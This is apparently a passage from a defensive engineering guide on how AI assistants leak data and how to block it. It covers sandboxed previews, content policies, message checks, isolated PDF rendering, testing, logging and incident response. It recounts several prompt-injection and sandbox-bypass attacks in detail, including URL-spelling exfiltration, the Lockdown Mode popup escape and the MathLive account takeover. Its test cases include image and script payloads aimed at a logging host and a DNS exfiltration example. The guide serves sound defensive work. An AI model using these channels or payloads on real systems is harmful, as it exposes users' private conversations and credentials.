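OpenAI's claim covers only quiet leaks through the URL itself. An agent that can type into a web page could still put a customer's record into a search box or comment form on a page it was allowed to open. Forms therefore need a separate control, such as asking the user before the agent submits one or using a browsing mode that doesn't allow typing.

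A company also has to apply the rule everywhere. ChatGPT's apps lacked the earlier version of the check, and Embrace The Red warns that developers at a large company may not know such a safeguard exists. The rule is easier to apply consistently if all products send their requests through one fetching service and no tool can reach the internet without it.

### How much a choice of address reveals

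The agent can still leak data through its choice of address. A choice among *N* permitted addresses reveals up to log₂ *N* bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question.

When each request can go to one of ten addresses, the choice of address reveals one digit of a six-digit login code (log₂ 10 ≈ 3.32 bits), so six requests reveal the whole code (log₂ 1,000,000 ≈ 19.9 bits). With a thousand addresses, each request reveals three digits (9.97 bits), so two requests are enough.

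Stealing longer data takes many more requests. A 1,200-byte email contains up to 9,600 bits, so sending it could take up to 964 requests at 9.97 bits each. Without the rule, one image address could carry the whole email. An attacker can reduce the number of requests by having the model summarise the email or pick out the important figures. The rule therefore protects well against bulk theft but poorly against the theft of passwords, codes and single facts, such as whether a company is about to be sold.

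The ZombieAgent attack extracted data through ChatGPT's choice of which addresses to open. OpenAI had responded to an earlier attack, ShadowLeak, by stopping ChatGPT from adding data to an address it was given. The security firm Radware got round this by supplying complete addresses. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes injected text that contained one address for each letter and digit, such as `example.com/a` and `example.com/7`, and a special token for spaces. ChatGPT spelled out the data by opening the matching addresses in order.

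Each request revealed one of 37 characters (26 letters, ten digits and a space), or log₂ 37 ≈ 5.2 bits. The phrase "meeting at noon" would take 15 requests. OpenAI responded by stopping ChatGPT from opening links from an email unless they appear in a well-known public index or the user has supplied them.

The fix made the attack harder to prepare, but the attack still works in principle because an attacker can get addresses into an index. Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. A bigger site could assign thousands of pages to whole words.

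The July 2026 attack on Claude's web-fetch tool spelled out a user's name through a chain of links and didn't need an index. The tool accepted addresses found in pages it had already fetched, so the attacker's site could supply new ones during the attack. A page can offer 26 links, one for each letter, and each link can lead to another page of 26 links. The server can create each new page when the request for it arrives.

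Removing that trust, as Anthropic did, is somewhat less convenient for the user, since Claude can't follow a reference from one page to another unless the second page's address also comes from a source that is still trusted. An application could still allow this for references found on hosts that pass the three-question audit, where an attacker can't publish pages.

### Limiting repeat visits

Rehberger suggests that instead of refusing repeat visits, the application could store each page for a few minutes and answer repeated requests from the stored copy. Either way, the attacker's server receives only the first request. Storing pages is better for users because the agent can still reread them.

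Suppose that an attacker has prepared indexed pages to steal a six-digit code. How much a limit on repeats helps depends on how many pages there are and what they mean:

| Attacker's arrangement | Pages needed | Requests | Effect of a limit on repeats |
|---|---|---|---|
| The same ten pages for every digit | 10 | 6 | Hides repeated digits |
| Ten pages for each position | 60 | 6 | None |
| A thousand pages for each half of the code | 2,000 | 2 | None |
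| One page for each binary digit | 20 | About 10 on average | None |

In the first arrangement, the limit lets the attacker get the whole code only if all six digits differ, which is true of 10 × 9 × 8 × 7 × 6 × 5 = 151,200 codes, or about 15% of them. In the last arrangement, the model writes the code as a binary number and opens a page for each 1. Twenty pages are enough because 2²⁰ = 1,048,576, which is more than the million possible codes. This arrangement also works even if the browser's requests arrive out of order, which is another obstacle Rehberger mentions.

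Even ten pages can be enough if the requests arrive in order. There are 10 × 9 × 8 × 7 × 6 × 5 × 4 × 3 = 1,814,400 ways to open eight of them without a repeat, more than the number of codes. The attack would fail more often because the model would have to follow a complicated table or run a small program, but a limit on repeats can't rule it out.

Limiting repeated fetches of the same page also wouldn't have stopped the attack on Claude, because every page in the chain had a new address. Rehberger suggests the limits as an extra obstacle for attackers, and they are worth having as one because a short-lived page cache takes few resources to run.

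A cap on automatic fetches limits leaks more firmly. If an agent makes exactly *R* fetches from *N* permitted addresses, the sequence reveals at most *R* × log₂ *N* bits, ignoring timing. Five fetches among a thousand addresses reveal at most about 50 bits, too few to leak a long document but enough for two login codes. The application can keep such codes from the model by excluding automated login emails from the mailbox search, which loses little because few users will ask about an expired code.

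If the application can keep copies of the pages in its index, it can give the agent a stored copy without sending a request to the site. The site's owner then learns nothing from which pages the agent reads. The copies may be out of date, which matters little for a manual but a lot for a price or a news story. The support company could use stored copies whenever a conversation contains customer records and allow live fetches in the separate mode that has no access to private data.

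## Isolating generated pages and previews

Some products are meant to run code that the model writes. A member of the support staff might ask the assistant for a refund calculator and expect a working page beside the chat. ChatGPT can preview HTML pages, interactive React components, diagrams and charts, according to OpenAI's *Working with writing blocks and code blocks in ChatGPT*. A sanitiser would remove the script that makes such a page work, so the application has to let the script run and limit what the script can access.

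An injection in a ticket can influence the calculator's code as easily as it can influence a summary. The page may also contain private data, because the conversation was part of the model's input when it wrote the code. The application therefore has to keep the script away from the user's account and stop it from sending the page's data elsewhere. It can do this with a separate domain, a sandboxed frame (an embedded page that the browser isolates from the page around it), a Content Security Policy for that frame, and a restricted channel for messages.

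### A domain with nothing to steal

If the chat page is at chat.example.com, the company could serve generated pages from preview-pages.example, a domain it uses for nothing else. The same-origin policy then stops a generated script from reading the chat page or its storage. The preview domain should set no login cookies and offer no account functions, so that a script with full control of the domain can't use it to steal a login or act on a user's account.

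A subdomain such as preview.example.com also has its own origin, but it gives weaker protection. Sites often set login cookies for all their subdomains, so the browser would send them to the preview server too. Companies also tend to write rules that trust every subdomain they own. Hacktron's *Pwning OpenAI Atlas Through Exposed Browser Internals* describes how such a rule in OpenAI's Atlas browser let any page under openai.com or chatgpt.com call powerful internal functions. The researchers found an XSS flaw on OpenAI's forum site that let them control the victim's tabs and capture login codes for other websites.

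### What the sandbox permits

The chat page embeds the calculator like this:

```
<iframe src="https://preview-pages.example/p/8f3k2"
        sandbox="allow-scripts"></iframe>
```

With an empty `sandbox` attribute, the browser refuses scripts, forms, popups and several other things. It also gives the page a throwaway origin that matches no other page. Each word in the attribute restores one ability:

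| Permission | What the page can do | For generated pages |
|---|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | Run JavaScript | Needed for anything interactive |
| `allow-same-origin` | Keep its real origin, with that origin's cookies and storage | Leave out, or give each page its own subdomain |
| `allow-popups` | Open new windows and tabs | Leave out |
| `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` | Open windows that the sandbox doesn't restrict | Never |
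| `allow-forms` | Submit forms | Only with `form-action 'none'` in the page's policy |
| `allow-top-navigation` | Send the whole tab to another address | Never |
| `allow-top-navigation-by-user-activation` | The same, after a click | Leave out |

Combining `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin` defeats the sandbox if the generated page shares the chat page's origin. A script in the generated page can delete the `sandbox` attribute from its own frame, then reload the frame without restrictions. Developers can make this mistake with `srcdoc`, because a page written into that attribute takes the origin of the page that contains it. If previews are served from a separate domain, the two settings don't expose the chat page, but previews on that domain can read each other's storage. A preview that has to save data, such as a calculator that remembers its settings, therefore needs its own subdomain.

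A generated page that can open popups or navigate the tab can leak data by including it in the address. A popup normally inherits the sandbox's limits, but the browser has already requested the address by the time they apply. A page that can navigate the whole tab can also replace the chat with a fake login page. Requiring a click first adds little protection, because people click on generated pages such as calculators in normal use.

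Leaving out `allow-forms` breaks some harmless pages, because the browser blocks the submission before the page's script can respond to it. With `allow-forms` and `form-action 'none'`, the script can run its calculation when the user presses the button, but the browser doesn't send the form anywhere. Willison's *iframe sandbox* (2024) is an online tool for trying out permissions, with a code editor beside the sandboxed result.

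### Lockdown Mode and the popup flaw

The sandbox for ChatGPT's HTML preview granted two unnecessary permissions, which also defeated a security setting called Lockdown Mode. OpenAI launched that setting for organisations in February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts in June, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (OpenAI, 2026). Lockdown Mode uses fixed rules to block ways for data to leave, rather than relying on the model to resist prompt injection.

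Under the restrictions listed in OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, ChatGPT reads only cached copies of web pages, may not show images in ordinary answers, and can't download files for analysis. Users can't allow code in the Canvas editing pane to access the network. Deep research and agent mode, in which ChatGPT works through long tasks by itself, are off. Personal accounts also lose live access to outside services where that access conflicts with these protections, while administrators of company workspaces choose which apps stay on.

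The setting doesn't affect memory, file uploads, conversation sharing or Codex's network access. Hostile text in an uploaded file can still distort an answer. OpenAI also warns that unforeseen combinations of features could still leak data, and the HTML preview turned out to be one such combination.

*Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) summarises a report by Alexey Bukhteyev of Check Point Research. ChatGPT put each preview inside two nested sandboxed frames and asked the user before letting the page contact an outside server. To control popups, it replaced the page's `window.open` function with one that asked for approval. But the sandbox still had the `allow-popups` and `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` permissions. A hostile page could create another frame inside itself, which had its own unmodified `window.open`. Anything opened with that function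 ran outside the sandbox and Lockdown Mode.

The worst case was ChatGPT Classic, the older desktop application, whose built-in browser opened popups without waiting for a click. An attacker could publish a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that anyone can configure and share. A victim only had to chat with it for the attacker to receive the victim's whole chat history. In other demonstrations, a popup with ChatGPT's icon offered a bogus update, and a fake login page collected passwords.

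OpenAI removed both permissions from the outer frame on September 18, 2026. This also blocks them in every frame inside it, because a nested frame can't have more permissions than the one around it. Check Point retested the attack, found that it no longer worked, and published a report on November 5 that describes no attacks on real users. OpenAI will shut down ChatGPT Classic on January 30, 2027, according to Clubic's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations*.

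Hostile code could get around the replaced function from inside, as it could with the network settings in Copilot's code sandbox. The browser, by contrast, enforces sandbox permissions from outside the page. If the sandbox blocks popups, links that open a new tab stop working, but the preview can pass the link's address to the chat page, which can apply the same checks it uses for links in answers.

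### A policy for the page inside

The sandbox doesn't limit which servers a page can contact, so the preview server has to send a policy with each page:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  sandbox allow-scripts;
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'unsafe-inline';
  style-src 'unsafe-inline';
  img-src data: blob:;
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none';
  frame-ancestors https://chat.example.com
```

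This policy allows inline script because the preview exists to run it, although the chat page's own policy forbids it. The previewed page has to contain everything it needs. The `sandbox` line keeps the limits in place if somebody opens a preview's address in its own tab.

Users lose maps, live data and code libraries from the web. The company can restore the libraries by keeping approved copies on its own server and adding that server to `script-src`. Asking the user before each outside connection, as ChatGPT may do, lets more pages work but has the same weakness as asking before loading an image.

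A script can also leak data by changing the address of its own frame, which the policy above doesn't stop. The chat page's policy can block this if its `frame-src` line names only `https://preview-pages.example`. A team should test that protection in each browser it supports. A script can also leak data through WebRTC, which browsers use for video calls, because `connect-src` doesn't govern WebRTC connections. The model should therefore include only the private data a generated page needs. For example, a refund calculator needs the refund rules but not customers' names.

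### Messages to the chat page

The calculator may need to tell the chat page how tall its frame should be. Browsers provide `postMessage` for this, which lets two pages exchange data even if neither can read the other. The chat page has to check who sent each message and what it contains:

```
window.addEventListener('message', event => {
  if (event.source !== preview.contentWindow) return;
  if (event.data?.type !== 'height') return;
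  const height = event.data.value;
  if (!Number.isFinite(height)) return;
  preview.style.height = Math.min(Math.max(height, 100), 2000) + 'px';
});
```

Here `preview` is the calculator's frame. The first check compares windows rather than origins because every sandboxed page's origin arrives as the string "null". The other checks accept only one kind of message, containing one number, and the last line keeps that number within limits. If the frame has moved to a hostile page, that page passes the first check but can still only change the height.

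When the chat page sends a message to the frame, it can't name a throwaway origin as the recipient, so it has to address the message to `"*"`, meaning whatever page is in the frame. It should never send a login token that way.

In October 2026 researchers at the security firm Parameter took over ChatGPT accounts through a message that the main page should have refused. Goyal (2026) explains in *Do the Math* that ChatGPT ran previews in a restricted frame on a different domain, which kept code in the preview from reading the main page. But when a conversation contained an interactive graph, ChatGPT loaded MathLive, a library for mathematical formulas, into the main page. MathLive listened for messages from any sender about its on-screen keyboard.

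The preview sent MathLive a new keyboard layout that contained HTML. MathLive passed the HTML through a function that marked it as trusted without sanitising it, then inserted it into the main page. The HTML created an unsandboxed frame with the chatgpt.com origin. ChatGPT's CSP blocked inline script in that frame but allowed scripts from YouTube, and an attacker could make one YouTube address return text of their choosing as script. That script could list the victim's conversations, read private ones and send them to an outside server.

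The attacker delivered all this in an ordinary shared conversation. At first the victim had to press the Preview button, but the researchers found they could mark the HTML so that ChatGPT opened the preview automatically. The request to open Copilot's HTML preview had worked similarly. An application should open previews of other people's content only after the user clicks, and neither the content nor the model should be able to change that.

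OpenAI received the report on October 18 and fixed the flaw on October 26. It paid $5,000, which Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, considered rather low for such a serious flaw. According to Infobae's *Un fallo de ChatGPT permitía acceder a conversaciones privadas* (2026), Parameter found no sign of attacks on real users, and MathLive has accepted only messages from its own origin by default since version 0.111.2. Check Point told The Hacker News that it had found a different flaw in the same component (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026).

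A nonce-only script policy would have blocked the YouTube script. The message listener is harder to catch in review because it came from the MathLive library, not OpenAI's own code. In Chrome's developer tools, `getEventListeners(window).message` lists the functions waiting for messages on a page. Reviewers should run it after using every feature, since MathLive's listener appeared only once a graph had loaded. Libraries that draw graphs can also go into a separate sandboxed frame, where an unsafe listener can do less harm.

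daily.dev summarises an attack on another AI application with the same weakness, in which both the sender and the receiver accepted any origin. A prompt in a link made the model produce HTML, and the attacker used the open channel to keep reading the conversation. The recommended fixes include the Cross-Origin-Opener-Policy header, which can cut a page's connection to the window that opened it.

### Interfaces supplied by tools

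Tools can also send an assistant complete interfaces, such as a booking form or a panel for managing permissions. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting assistants to tools. *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025) proposed an extension to it called MCP Apps. The proposal came from maintainers at OpenAI and Anthropic and the creators of an earlier project, MCP-UI, and became stable in January 2026.

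A tool's server declares an interface under an address that begins with `ui://`. The application, which the standard calls the host, fetches the HTML and displays it. According to the Model Context Protocol documentation, web hosts typically display it in a sandboxed frame inside the conversation. The interface lists the outside origins it needs to load from and requests the microphone or camera if it needs them. It exchanges messages with the host in JSON-RPC, a format for requests and replies, so the host can inspect and record them in one place.

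The declaration protects users if the tool's author is honest and someone else injects code into the interface, because the browser will block origins that the author didn't list. It offers much less protection against a dishonest author, who can list their own server. The host should check the declared origins against its own allow-list and refuse any that aren't on it.

The message channel also carries more authority than the calculator's, since an interface may ask the host to act. Suppose the support company adds an outside supplier's delivery tracker, which needs an order number. The host shouldn't send it the rest of the conversation, and if the tracker asks the host to email a customer, the host should treat the request as untrusted. A host can avoid this work by not supporting MCP Apps. According to the Model Context Protocol overview, the tools then return text instead.

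### Pages rendered on a server

When an assistant exports a page to PDF or makes a thumbnail of it, the page often opens in a browser on a server, where the protections in the user's browser don't apply. A script in the page may be able to contact machines on the company's internal network. On many cloud services, it may also be able to reach an internal address that returns access keys. If the page exploits a flaw in the server's browser, the attacker's code runs on the server.

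NebuSec, a security firm, reported an attack of this kind on Meta's Muse assistant in November 2026. Muse gives each user a virtual machine (a simulated computer) in the cloud and uses Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, to make PDFs. TechRadar's *Meta Muse can be hacked to access user private chats* reports that the researchers got Muse to export a hostile web page, which let them run code in the assistant's environment. They got past Sentinel, which monitors outgoing traffic, and extracted conversations and stored memories, which they could also alter. They then used flaws in the Linux kernel to take full control of the virtual machine and obtain the login credentials stored there.

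Meta fixed the flaws before NebuSec published, and nobody has reported real attacks. The researchers didn't show a way into other users' machines, so giving each user a separate one seems to have contained the damage. Within the machine, the PDF browser ran too close to the assistant's data. A safer design starts a new container for each export, with nothing in it except the page:

```
docker run --rm --network none --read-only --tmpfs /tmp \
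  --cap-drop ALL --security-opt seccomp=chrome.json \
  --user 1000:1000 --memory 1g \
  -v "$PWD/job:/job" page-to-pdf
```

The `job` folder holds the HTML and receives the PDF. The file `chrome.json` lists the system calls that Chromium's own sandbox needs. Developers often turn this sandbox off with `--no-sandbox` because it won't start in a container. Doing so removes the first layer that a browser exploit has to get through. The service that starts the container should also stop it after, say, 30 seconds.

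Removing network access altogether is safer than blocking only web traffic. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a path to the internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code, through which one malicious prompt could leak messages and uploaded files. According to Clubic, the path used DNS, the system that looks up server names. A lookup for `meeting-at-noon.example.com` sends the text "meeting-at-noon" to whoever runs the name server for example.com, even if the machine can't open a web page. If an exported page needs outside pictures, the application can fetch approved ones beforehand and put them in the folder.

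Many products can avoid the server by letting users print the preview from their own browser. The frame then needs `allow-modals`, which permits the print dialog but also lets the page show alert boxes. Layouts vary slightly between browsers, which matters for an invoice template but rarely for a calculator.

### Checklist for accepting a preview feature

A reviewer can accept the feature when all of these are true:

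- The preview domain sets no cookies, and no other system gives it special trust.
- A preview opened in its own tab has the same limits as one in the chat.
- The `sandbox` attribute contains `allow-scripts`, and somebody has written down a reason for any other permission.
- A test page can't read the chat page, open a window from a nested frame, navigate the tab or contact a test server.
- Every message listener on the main page checks the sender and the content, including listeners that libraries add.
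- Shared and retrieved content never opens in a preview without the user's click.
- Any setting that promises to restrict network access also covers previews, or turns them off.
- The desktop and mobile applications pass the same checks as the website.
- Interfaces from tools get only the origins, devices and data that the host has approved.
- Browsers on servers run without a network connection, credentials or other users' files.
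- The team can switch previews off for everyone without releasing a new version.

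## Testing the application and judging the result

Suppose a tester asks the support assistant to put an outside image in its answer, and no image appears. Either the display blocked the image or the model did not write it. If the model did not write it, the display has not been tested, and an attacker with better wording may still get the model to write the image. The tester should therefore first test the display alone, with fixed text in place of the model's answer, and then test the whole path from a hostile document to an outside server.

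Both tests need a web server, here called log.example.net, that the tester owns and that records every request. The tester has to judge the result from the server's log, because what appears on screen can be misleading. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a demonstration against Microsoft's Copilot Chat in which no picture appeared in the answer, but the image request still reached the researchers' server.

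### Testing the display with fixed answers

The tester replaces the call to the model with a function that returns prepared text in pieces:

```
const cases = {
  markdownImage: a => `![Logo](${a})`,
  referenceImage: a => `![Logo][1]\n\n[1]: ${a}`,
  htmlImage: a => `<img src="${a}">`,
  videoPoster: a => `<video poster="${a}"></video>`,
  prefetch: a => `<link rel="prefetch" href="${a}">`,
  eventHandler: () => `<img src="/logo.png" onload="document.title='Changed'">`
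};

async function* fakeModel(text, size) {
  for (let i = 0; i < text.length; i += size) {
    yield text.slice(i, i + size);
    await new Promise(done => setTimeout(done, 50));
  }
}
```

With `size` set to 1, the answer arrives one character at a time. The pause gives the browser time to act on a partial answer. In SearchLeak, the browser sent the image request at this stage. Each run puts its own number in the address, such as `https://log.example.net/run-0417`, so a single line in the log identifies the combination that failed.

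A full set of cases varies four things:

| What varies | Values to test | Failure to look for |
|---|---|---|
| Element | Image, CSS background, font, video poster, frame, prefetch, `meta` refresh, form, link | A request without a click, or a link to an unapproved host |
| Syntax | Inline and reference-style Markdown, raw HTML, a diagram label, a chart's data address | Markup that one notation lets through and another doesn't |
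| Streaming state | Whole answer, single characters, stopped midway, reopened from history | A request that leaves before the answer is complete |
| Host application | Website, each office program, desktop and mobile applications, notification emails, exported PDFs | A result that differs from the website's |

Any script that runs is also a failure, even if it only changes the page's title. The test set should include ordinary answers, such as a lesson on writing HTML. If the sanitiser removes the code samples, users will complain, and a colleague may loosen its rules to restore the samples.

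The tester should also run every case on a page with no defences, to confirm that it produces a request or runs its script. Otherwise a typing mistake in the test, or a logging server that is down, looks like a pass. It also helps to repeat the set on a test copy of the application with the Content Security Policy turned off. If a request arrives only then, the sanitiser let through an attack that the policy had been blocking, and the same attack could work on any page with a looser policy.

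Testing twenty answers in four streaming states and five applications takes 20 × 4 × 5 = 400 runs. At ten seconds per run, a browser-automation tool finishes in a little over an hour, so the team can repeat the tests before each release and after each update to the parser, sanitiser or diagram library. The same text normally produces the same page, so one clean run per combination is good evidence. The streaming cases depend on timing, so they are worth running several times with different piece sizes.

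### Testing the whole path with planted secrets

The second test uses the real model in a copy of the application that holds only made-up data. The tester puts a different dummy secret in each data store listed in the inventory and a hostile instruction in each untrusted source, including the error messages that tools return. A test user then asks ordinary questions.

Any request to log.example.net is a failure, whatever it carries. The tester should also search the application's other outgoing traffic for the secrets, since the model may have sent them elsewhere. A plain search would miss an encoded copy. Base64 works on groups of three bytes, so a secret in the middle of a longer text can appear in three different forms, depending on where it starts. This function lists them, along with the plain and hexadecimal forms:

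```
import base64

def traces(secret):
    raw = secret.encode()
    found = {secret, raw.hex()}
    for shift in range(3):
        text = base64.b64encode(b"\0" * shift + raw).decode()
        start = (0, 2, 3)[shift]
        end = (None, -3, -2)[(shift + len(raw)) % 3]
        found.add(text[start:end])
    return found
```

Secrets of about 20 random letters and digits work well, because they rarely match anything by accident and survive URL encoding unchanged. The search still misses a secret that the model has translated, reversed or sent one letter at a time.

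The logging server has to keep listening after the chat closes, because some leaks only appear later. In the ReLeak attacks that Simonovich disclosed, Microsoft's background services sent data out of saved documents after the conversation had ended. Between July and November 2026, the industrial security firm Dragos sent AI providers nearly two million prompts containing bait credentials and unique web addresses. Cybernews' *AI routers are leaking your passwords. Here's the proof* reports that somebody opened some of those addresses months after the only request that had contained them.

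Dragos tested companies that run models, but its method can also be used to test applications that display answers. Network Security Magazine's *OpenRouter Drops 3 Providers After Researchers Catch Months of Prompt Theft* explains that each secret existed in only one prompt, so any use of it proved that somebody had read that prompt. Dragos found signs that attackers had broken into at least three hosting providers. An application's tester should therefore include control runs with planted secrets and web addresses but no hostile instruction. If someone uses a secret from a control run, the leak may have happened at the model's supplier or a reseller, where no sanitiser can stop it.

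### What TicketOracle measured

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian found that the result of a whole-path test depends heavily on the model. For their experiment, run in April 2026 and published in August, they built TicketOracle, a concert-ticket site whose assistant had one tool. The tool made the site's server fetch any address without checking it. The server also ran an administration service that the tool could reach but outsiders couldn't.

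In four scenarios, the attacker typed instructions into the chat to check whether a port was open, read user records, delete a user, or make a change through a page that returned an empty response. In the fifth, the instructions were in a concert review, and an innocent user asked about the concert. The table gives the number of successes in ten trials. The last column comes from a version whose system prompt listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others.

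| Model | Port probe | User records | Deletion | Empty response | Planted review, stricter prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

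Attacks on the same application succeeded in all 40 direct trials with Llama and in none with GPT-5.2 or Claude. A developer who tested only with Claude would have approved an assistant with an unrestricted fetch tool, and the flaw would have appeared when somebody switched to a cheaper model.

The stricter prompt stopped every direct attack on every model. Against the planted review, successes fell from five to none with GPT-oss but rose from six to ten with Llama. The review used with the stricter prompt also contained a false claim that the list of addresses had been extended, which may explain part of Llama's rise. In both cases the list was only text in the prompt. A check in the tool's own code would have rejected the address whichever model wrote it.

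These rates measure requests made by a server, so they can't predict how often a model will write an image that leaks data. Except in the empty-response scenario, which the researchers checked in a server log, a trial counted as a success only if the assistant also repeated the result to the user, so a deletion it never mentioned would not have counted. In a test for data theft, the request alone has to count as a success, because the data has already been sent.

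The zeros are also weaker evidence than zeros from ten fresh conversations would be, because the researchers ran each set of ten trials in a single conversation, where Claude's earlier refusals probably influenced the later ones. As the prompt repeated, its refusals shrank from long explanations almost to single words.

### How many clean attempts are enough

Suppose that an attack succeeds with probability *p* on each attempt and that the attempts are independent. The chance of seeing *n* failures in a row is (1 − p)^n. After *n* clean attempts, a tester can rule out, at 95% confidence, every *p* that would make this chance smaller than 5%. The highest rate that remains possible is:

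p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

If 300 test attacks all fail, the 95% upper confidence bound on the success rate is 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099, or about 1%. At that rate, an attacker who makes 100 attempts has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once, and can make them in a few seconds by emailing 100 employees.

| Clean attempts | Highest rate still possible | Attacker's chance in 100 attempts at that rate |
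|---|---|---|
| 10 | 26% | Over 99.9% |
| 100 | 3.0% | 95% |
| 300 | 1.0% | 63% |
| 1,000 | 0.30% | 26% |
| 5,840 | 0.05% | 5% |

A team that wants to hold the attacker's chance to 5% therefore needs almost 6,000 clean attempts, and has to repeat them whenever the vendor changes the model. Even then, 5% understates the risk, because three hundred repetitions of one wording test only that wording, while a real attacker studies the refusals and tries something else. Each attempt should at least start a new conversation and use a new wording. The whole-path test is most useful for finding outlets that nobody had listed. When it finds one, the team should close it with a fixed rule and add the leaking answer to the display tests, where one run can check it.

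### What to log and what to look for

After release, an investigator will need to reconstruct how a piece of outside text led to a request. For each session, the application should record:

- the documents, emails and pages that the model read, and who supplied them
- each tool call with its full arguments, and whether a person approved it
- the model's answer before sanitising
- each request that a server sent, with the complete address
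- each memory that the assistant saved or deleted, and the text that led to the change
- violations reported under the Content Security Policy

Few people should have access to these logs, which also contain hostile markup. A log viewer that displays old answers as HTML can run an attacker's script in an administrator's browser, so it should show the answers as plain text.

Products often leave out records that an investigator needs. In 2024 criminals were using stolen Amazon Web Services (AWS) keys to run chatbots at the owners' expense. Krebs on Security's *A Single Cloud Compromise Can Feed an Army of AI Sex Bots* (2024) reports that none of the victims studied had turned on full logging, and that the default logs omitted prompts and answers, so the victims couldn't see what the criminals had done. As of April 2026, Microsoft 365 Copilot also lacked audit entries for memory changes. Embrace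 The Red shows that the user saw a "Memory updated" notice in small type below the prompt, but an administrator investigating a complaint weeks later couldn't search for it.

Several patterns in outgoing requests suggest a leak:

| Pattern | What it may mean |
|---|---|
| A long run of letters and digits in an address | Data in Base64 or hexadecimal |
| One address inside another | A permitted server passing data on |
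| Many short addresses on one host that differ by a character | Data spelled out through the choice of page |
| Lookups of long, unusual server names | Data leaving through DNS |
| A request from a document service when no user is active | An address hidden in a saved file |

Varonis advises companies to look for incoming Copilot Search links whose `q` parameter contains encoded HTML tags or instructions to put data into an image address.

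Harmless traffic can show any of these patterns, so a person needs to check any alarms based on them. Policy reports miss leaks through approved hosts, because the browser reports only what it blocks. A planted credential gives a much clearer signal. If the company keeps a fake access key in a mailbox that the assistant can search, nobody has a legitimate reason to use the key, so any attempt to use it is an incident.

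### First steps after a leak

Stolen keys need the fastest response. hrbrmstr (2026), in *Somebody Is Hunting For Your AI API Keys*, describes decoy servers from which thieves took 53 planted AWS keys over six days. They tried to use each key on Amazon's AI service within ten seconds. No human team can react that quickly, but every further minute gives the thief more time. A workable order is:

1. Switch off the outlet for everyone, whether it is images, previews or the fetch tool, so that new secrets can't follow the old ones.
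2. At the same time, revoke every password and access key that the model could read in the affected sessions.
3. Look for accounts that the thief has created. In the Dragos experiment, according to UA.News' *Study finds secret leaks in AI service chains*, thieves added their own users to the cloud accounts to keep their access. Revoking the stolen key doesn't remove those users.
4. Copy the logs and the hostile text before a deletion schedule removes them.
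5. Search other people's mail, tickets and saved memories for the same text, and delete any memory that it produced.
6. Work out what left. If the logs lack complete addresses, assume that everything the model read in the session is gone, and tell the people affected.
7. Add the leaking answer to the display tests, and turn the outlet back on only when they pass.

### Why severity scores disagree

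Teams usually use a flaw's severity rating to decide how quickly to fix it, but ratings for this kind of flaw vary widely. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the company's advisory on SearchLeak, labels the flaw "Critical" but scores it 6.5 out of 10, which is medium. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, which is high.

Both numbers come from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), a public formula. The change history in CVEFeed's *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) shows that the two organisations agreed on every input except whether the attack needs an action by the victim. In CVSS 3.1 the score for this flaw is the sum of an impact part and an exploitability part, rounded up to one decimal place:

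```
impact         = 6.42 × 0.56                       = 3.595
exploitability = 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × u

action needed:     u = 0.62   3.595 + 2.835 = 6.430  →  6.5
no action needed:  u = 0.85   3.595 + 3.887 = 7.482  →  7.5
```

The victim had to click a link, so Microsoft's input is correct. The "Critical" label comes from Microsoft's own scale, which is separate from CVSS. Some reports confused the two scales. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool*, for example, gave the rating as "10/10 critical".

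A serious leak can have a low CVSS score. The font flaw that let a shared Word document steal a victim's email also carries Microsoft's "Critical" label, but STAR Labs' *M365 Copilot* (2026) lists its score as 5.3. SearchLeak scored 6.5, and the difference comes entirely from attack complexity, which Microsoft rated as high for the font flaw, lowering that input's value from 0.77 to 0.44. CVSS has only three levels for loss of confidentiality, and its base score doesn't account for how many people use a product or what they keep in it. A team that sorts its repairs by that score alone would put a flaw that exposes whole mailboxes behind many routine bugs. It is more useful to ask what data the model can reach, how many clicks the attack needs, and whether a fixed rule failed or only the model's judgement.

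### When vendors decline to fix a leak

Some vendors don't accept that these leaks are vulnerabilities. Checkmarx reported the Copilot Chat image leak in October 2025, and Microsoft closed the report in November without a fix. Microsoft replied that the attack needed more than one non-default action by the user and didn't reproduce reliably, and that the product displayed warnings. It also assumed that developers review and trust the code they choose to run.

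After four days, Google closed a different report, about Gemini links that send data when the user clicks them. It called the problem infeasible to fix and said the risk fell below its threshold for a security bug. Willison notes that Google's bug-reporting page listed data theft through prompt injection as a known issue in Antigravity. Google said it was working on a fix but wouldn't pay rewards for further reports. Cursor also called the attack in Zenity's report a known issue.

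Google's position on links has some merit. Gemini would be of little use for research without links, and Checkmarx accepts the answer as long as Google warns users about the risk. Allowing images is harder to excuse, because an application can block them with little downside, as Gemini does. Microsoft's point that the attack doesn't reproduce reliably is weak, because an attacker can keep trying. Its assumption about trusted code is reasonable for a program that a developer chooses to run, but a comment in a downloaded file can carry an injection even if the developer only asks for a summary.

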